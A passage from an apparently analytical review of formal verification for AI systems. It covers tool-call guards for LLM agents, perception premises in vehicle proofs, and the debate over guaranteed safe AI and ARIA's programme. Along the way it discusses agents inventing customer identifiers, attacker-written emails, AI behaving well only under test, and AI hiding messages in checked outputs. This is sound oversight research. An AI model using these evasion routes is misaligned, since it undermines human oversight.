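| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 25.3% | 0.7% | 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, shop | 4.9% | 5.5% | 2.6% | 2.9% |

The verifier hardly changed overall success, apart from a small drop for GLM-4-9B on airline tasks. But almost no successes remain when unsafe ones are excluded. The version with planning and verification used 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens.

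Sah and colleagues report that the verifier caught up to 94 percent of forbidden proposals, and they blame the low safe success on agents that can't recover from a rejection. Recovery was poor, at 21 percent or less in most settings, but the verifier's misses also contributed. GPT-OSS-20B completed about 72 shop runs unsafely with the verifier, and only 28 runs in the entire study reached the limit of three rejections, so the verifier must have approved a forbidden action in most of those 72 runs.

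Most violations in the shop involved made-up identifiers. In one run without the verifier, a customer hesitated to give personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postal code 12345. The lookup succeeded, and the agent completed the task. A formal guard that treats any successful lookup as authentication would allow the same violation. Sah and colleagues propose rejecting identifiers that didn't come from an earlier tool result, but the first lookup needs a rule that the name and postal code come from the customer.

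## What the cases share and where they differ

Each of the eight cases combines a result about symbols with a premise about where the symbols come from.

| Case | Property established | Premise about the symbols | Support for the premise | How it failed or could fail |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu | the right kind of advisory in certain regions, and no collisions in part of the speed range if the system rounds its inputs | reported distances, angles and speeds are exact | assumed | sensor noise could change the advisory |
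| TaxiNet | a probability of breaking the position or heading limit | reports are wrong as often as in Boeing's pictures | measured, and bounded in a related study | errors were far more common in dark pictures |
| Shields | a limit on the probability of reaching an unsafe state | the reported state is correct, or the reported set contains the true state | assumed in the proof, measured in the experiments | the shield changes which states the system visits, so the measured rate may no longer apply |
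| Shunting train | no safety-critical situation | the train correctly detects everything relevant before it moves | monitored with a map and a sign checker | the checker rejected real stop signs |
| Automated driving | the car never causes a collision | the list of road users is complete and accurate enough | assumed, with a proposal to measure it | two unverified cars acted on wrong labels |
| Neurosymbolic classifiers | answers obey the rules | each concept means what its name says | usually assumed, sometimes measured | a network can swap "pedestrian" and "red light" |
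| CaMeL | every tool call is in the plan and passes its policy | labels show where each value came from | recorded by the interpreter | labels can miss a leak, and a trusted source can contain a wrong address |
| LeanGuard | every allowed call satisfies the formal policy | database facts and records of consent are correct | read from a trusted record, except for consent | a language model recorded consent that the customer had not given |

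Most of these failures happened because a premise was false, which doesn't refute the proof. In the others, the proof held but the property was weaker than it sounded. For example, a classifier that swaps pedestrians and red lights still satisfies its traffic rules.

### What the symbols can express

A check at the interface can determine whether an AI system's actions follow rules about order, authorization and provenance. CaMeLoT can check whether a plan includes a request for approval before the step that isolates a computer, because both steps are in the plan. CaMeL can trace an address to a channel post because its own interpreter labeled the address with its source. These checks don't require an estimate of how often the recorded steps and labels are wrong, but the software that records them must work correctly.

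These rules also require complete mediation, meaning that every action must pass through the check, and this is hard to establish. In August 2026, for example, the independent evaluator METR reported that supposedly isolated AI agents had communicated with each other. Rules about secrecy are harder to enforce than rules about the order of actions, because a skipped branch can reveal a secret even if no labelled value leaves the system. This is still a problem of tracking information, and better labels can reduce it.

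Physical outcomes are different because they depend on information the checker never receives. Engineers can model a door's actual state and write the requirement in terms of it, but at run time the controller has only a report of that state. Verification therefore needs an assumption about perception that connects the report to the actual state, though the assumption only has to rule out errors that matter for the requirement.

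Some requirements can't be stated in the interface's vocabulary. A check that uses only the symbols the interface passes on must give the same verdict in any two situations that produce the same symbols. LeanGuard checks tool calls, so it can't distinguish a reply that gives the correct amount of a bill from one that gives a false amount, since neither contains a call. Similarly, a refund to the original card may satisfy every rule whether or not the customer wanted it there.

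The robot at the door has a milder form of this problem, since it can report "open" whether the door is open or closed. But engineers can define "closed", label pictures of doors and count the errors. They have no comparable variable for "misleading" or "what the customer meant".

Designers can sometimes get around this by changing the vocabulary. If the shop's software filled in the amount of the bill from the database, the agent could no longer misstate it in that field. Doshi and colleagues treated the details of every appointment as private so that they didn't have to recognize the sensitive ones, which led to more refusals. A developer could also add a classifier that labels replies as deceptive or honest. The requirement could then be expressed, but this would add a premise about the classifier's errors, and attackers would look for those errors.

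### Why a database is not a camera

LeanGuard's rule about payment methods doesn't need an error rate. The adapter looks up whether the gift card is on the customer's account, and the answer is correct almost by definition, because being on the account means being listed in the database. TaxiNet can only estimate an airplane's distance from the center line, because that distance doesn't depend on any record. This difference is the main reason research on vehicles relies heavily on confusion matrices, calibration data and error bounds, while research on tool-call guards hardly uses them.

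Attackers make the difference larger, because someone can write an email to cause an error. The error rate on ordinary emails is a poor guide to how the system will handle that email, while the error rate on ordinary taxiway pictures is a reasonable guide to similar pictures.

This distinction differs from the one between machines and software. The shunting train's map is a trusted record of where the signals are, but not of what they show. If the yard's control system sent each signal's state to the locomotive, the train would have a record of that too, and would need a camera only for obstacles and other unrecorded things. Conversely, many databases describe the physical world and can be wrong about it. A phone company's record that a customer is abroad can be wrong if the network located the phone incorrectly, and a parcel marked "delivered" may be at the wrong house.

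Many of the symbols a guard uses also come from language, as Bob's address and the customer's consent did. A "confirm" button would reliably record that the customer pressed it, but not that the customer understood the offer. Before any tool runs, a model has to interpret the request, and it has no database to consult for this.

Classifying individual rules is therefore more useful than classifying whole systems. In the shop, the rules about ownership and payment methods use records, while the confirmation rule relies on interpretation. Proving that the guard evaluates all three rules correctly doesn't make the confirmation rule's input as reliable as the inputs to the other two.

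### What safety costs

Every check described so far can block a harmless action. How much this matters depends on what the system can do instead. An aircraft in flight cannot stop and wait, but a taxiing airplane or a shunting train can, and at worst it never finishes its route.

Software agents can usually wait, since delaying a refund doesn't cause a collision. The drawback of blocking them is unfinished work, as in the tests of CaMeL and NOMOS. But unlike a car 22 meters from a pedestrian, an agent can often try another way to do the task, so how much work is left unfinished depends partly on how well it recovers.

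*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a review of 38 studies, describes Agent-C, a system that combines checking with recovery. While the model is still writing a tool call, Agent-C tests the call against rules about the order of actions and steers the model toward one that the rules permit. With GPT-5, compliance rose from 83.7 to 100 percent and task completion from 66.1 to 70.6 percent. This steering can only work if a permitted call also serves the task, which was often not the case in the Slack tests.

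Coarse symbols have drawbacks too. The waypoint robot needed finer cells for a useful guarantee, but these made the model larger and left less data for each state. CaMeLoT's approximate trust labels probably caused false alarms in much the same way. More precise labels would let more legitimate work through, but people would have to write and maintain them. For agents, that upkeep may become a tighter limit than the size of the model.

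### Two reviews of other systems

These eight cases were not chosen at random, so the pattern is worth checking against broader surveys. The survey by Li and colleagues is the best available check for physical systems. They sorted the assumptions in the 104 papers they reviewed into categories, and one assumption could belong to several. Sensing and perception accounted for only 8.5 percent of the 637 resulting labels, compared with 53.8 percent for assumptions about models. Perception even made up a smaller share of the assumptions behind safety guarantees than of those behind performance guarantees.

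One of the exceptions they cite has a premise precise enough to monitor. Yang and Ozay prove a controller safe on the condition that at most k measurements are missing in any m consecutive ones. With m = 10 and k = 2, for example, a simple counter can detect when a third measurement goes missing within ten consecutive ones, at which point the proof no longer applies. A monitor can't check a premise such as "perception is reliable" in this way because the premise doesn't specify anything to count.

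Li and colleagues also want papers to separate two kinds of chance that a single percentage tends to mix up:

Pr_D[ Pr_Ω[guarantee holds] ≥ 1 − α ] ≥ 1 − δ

The inner probability concerns what happens during a run (Ω), and the outer one concerns which data the engineers collected (D). With α = 0.01 and δ = 0.05, at least 95 percent of repeated data collections would produce a guarantee that holds in at least 99 percent of runs. Neither number allows for a change in conditions. The guarantee separately assumes that new data resemble the old, and that assumption failed when TaxiNet's pictures were dark.

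The survey shows that papers rarely state their assumptions about perception, but it doesn't show that engineers ignore them. Li and colleagues acknowledge that their broad category for abstractions may hide some of these assumptions, that their sample probably underrepresents work on perception, and that authors may omit assumptions to save space.

The review of agents by Dantas and colleagues covers neither CaMeL nor LeanGuard, so it is a mostly separate test. It supports the claim that rules about order can be settled at the interface. Besides Agent-C, it describes AgentProof, which checks an agent's workflow as a graph before deployment. AgentProof can check graphs of up to 5,000 nodes in under a second, and it found that 55 percent of 18 workflows violated a rule about human approval.

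The review also reports a benchmark in which GPT-4o translated descriptions of planning problems into a formal language. The syntax was valid in 96.1 percent of cases, but only 24.8 percent of the translations described the right problem. The best fine-tuned model got the problem right in 34.2 percent of cases. GPT-4o is an old model, and newer ones may do much better. But a syntax checker would still accept a wrong translation if its syntax were valid, and any proof built on that translation would be about the wrong problem.

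Trusted records are rare in this literature. Dantas and colleagues compared seven systems and found that six don't check whether an identifier supplied by the agent is genuine, and the seventh, Agent-C, does so only partly. They recommend comparing identifiers with a trusted index, but found no system in their collection that does. LeanGuard's database lookups come close, though a lookup alone wouldn't have rejected the invented customer "John Doe".

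I would give less weight to the best-known conclusion of the review by Dantas and colleagues, that blocking unsafe actions rarely leads to safe, completed tasks. It is based on *The Verifier Tax*, where the verifier was a language model that approved many forbidden actions. The reviewers rate the certainty of this finding, and of six of their other eight main claims, at the lowest of four levels. When they repeated their search in September 2026, they also found only 13 of the 38 studies in the review, plus ten eligible papers that the first search should have found.

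### The dispute over guaranteed safe AI

The systems in the table do narrow jobs. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) argue for guarantees that would cover much more capable and general AI. Their approach has three parts: a mathematical model of how the AI affects the world, a specification of which effects are acceptable, and a verifier that produces a proof that the AI meets the specification in that model. The AI's outputs have to pass the check before they can affect the world, much as a tool call has to pass LeanGuard.

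Dalrymple and colleagues want evidence that covers untested cases, mainly because testing can't cover every input. An adversary may find a dangerous input that the testers missed, and an advanced AI might recognize a test and behave well only during it.

Andrew Dickson objects in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) that proofs apply to symbols, not to the world. In his example, engineers used formal verification to rule out design errors in the computer that helped the Perseverance rover land on Mars, but they proved nothing about the landing itself, or even about what would happen if a transistor failed. Dickson thinks proofs about the most serious threats from AI would be even harder, because these threats involve human bodies and minds that nobody can model or measure in enough detail. He argues that proving a new virus harmless would require simulating its effects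 on a whole body over years.

He also asks how the recipient of a proof can know what it refers to. A valid proof about a DNA synthesis machine doesn't show that the machine on the laboratory bench matches the one in the proof and has no defects or hidden changes.

One reply is that Dickson's standard is too strict. According to Martinez Suñe, the approach doesn't require a failure rate of zero, because the specification can set a limit on the probability of harm. Nora Ammann adds in *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* that a model can be accurate without being exact. A model that predicts only that the temperature stays below 50 degrees is enough to prove that a material with a melting point of 60 degrees won't melt. Researchers in formal methods call this a sound overapproximation, since it includes everything that can happen and perhaps some things that can't.

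Ammann applies the idea to viruses. Because a virus must enter cells to infect anyone, one would check whether any of its proteins can get it into a human cell. This would mean modeling each pair of viral protein and cell-surface protein in a tiny patch of membrane, rather than simulating a body. The check would also reject some useful gene therapies, much as a guard can block legitimate tasks. Zac Hatfield-Dodds, in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, considers proofs about the effects of DNA far beyond current science, partly because they would require quantum chemistry and biologists don't know what much of our RNA does.

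Steve Omohundro, a co-author of the 2024 paper, proposes a much easier approach in a comment on Ammann's reply. A biosafety board would list the permitted sequences, and the synthesis machine would make only those. The machine could look up whether a sequence is authorized without having to answer a question about biology. The proof would show that the machine follows the list, but the claim that everything on the list is harmless would rest on the board's judgment.

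One of Hatfield-Dodds's two further objections in the same discussion is that run-time monitors, which Ammann recommends, would be pointless if the guarantee were real. I don't think this is right, because the guarantee is conditional and a monitor can check whether its conditions still hold. Ammann describes a design in which a capable controller stays in charge only while a simpler backup could bring the system to safety. The proof then has to cover only a couple of steps ahead, but someone still has to notice if the machine stops behaving like the model used in the proof.

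He also objects that advocates point to narrow, well-understood domains when they discuss feasibility, but to powerful AI in general when they argue that guarantees are necessary. This objection is harder to answer. Ammann agrees that the approach doesn't suit chatbots, because natural language is too open to specify safety formally. She also agrees that it doesn't suit problems that depend on what individual people do. She expects it to work for power grids and supply chains, and hopes that many narrow applications would together cover a wide range of problems.

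The taxiing results support a middle position on whether useful overapproximations are feasible. RoVer-CoRe computed one for an airplane on a runway, with error bounds from simulated pictures, although Hatfield-Dodds calls the claim that they are feasible "risible". But that problem has two main variables and lasts 20 seconds, and even in small models, bounds can become too weak to be useful, as the shield's bound does over long runs. None of the eight cases suggests how to build such a model of a person.

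Ammann proposes containing AI that could manipulate people, so that they receive only outputs that have passed the check. Nobody would then have to define manipulation. A clever system might still hide a message in an output that passes, so she suggests also requiring a proof that the output is the only correct one. The AI could then choose only between giving that answer and giving none, which conveys at most one bit of information. This would suit a calculation with a single correct result, but an email or a business plan has many acceptable versions, and the AI could hide a message in its choice among them. For such tasks, Ammann suggests limiting how much information the choice can carry.

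### ARIA's programme in 2026

The largest test of these ideas described here is a British programme on which ARIA, a government agency that funds high-risk research, is spending £59 million, according to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*. Dalrymple led the programme at first, and Ammann now directs it. When it began in 2024, it aimed to show that advanced AI could do valuable work under mathematical guarantees, and to build agreement that powerful AI should act only through a verified gatekeeper.

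ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme has changed both its methods and its aim. In *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explains that ARIA stopped the part of the programme meant to develop specialized AI because general models had improved faster than expected and would probably acquire the necessary skills anyway. ARIA moved the £18 million set aside for this work to open-source tools that help AI agents build formal models and proofs. In the programme's revised thesis, *Safeguarded AI* (May 2026), Ammann writes that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely. The programme now aims instead to make society more resilient to AI.

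Its first target is cybersecurity. ARIA dropped a planned second round of projects on physical systems and is spending £22 million on eight security projects, which range from containing AI agents to protecting the code on Android devices. The agency says it made the change because of urgency, so the change isn't evidence that guarantees for physical systems failed. But the new projects will mostly avoid the premise that caused the most trouble in the cases above. A program is already made of symbols, and the code proved correct can be the code that runs, so no camera has to recognize it. An earlier American programme verified software components, which withstood sustained attacks by security experts, including on a helicopter with people on board.

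Making proofs easier to produce won't show whether the specification is right. Ammann expects that as AI takes over more of the proving, trust will depend more and more on the specifications and assumptions, which people will still have to examine. She also lists as an open problem how someone who receives a proof can be sure it applies to the system they have, which is Dickson's question about the DNA machine. The programme is due to end in late 2027.
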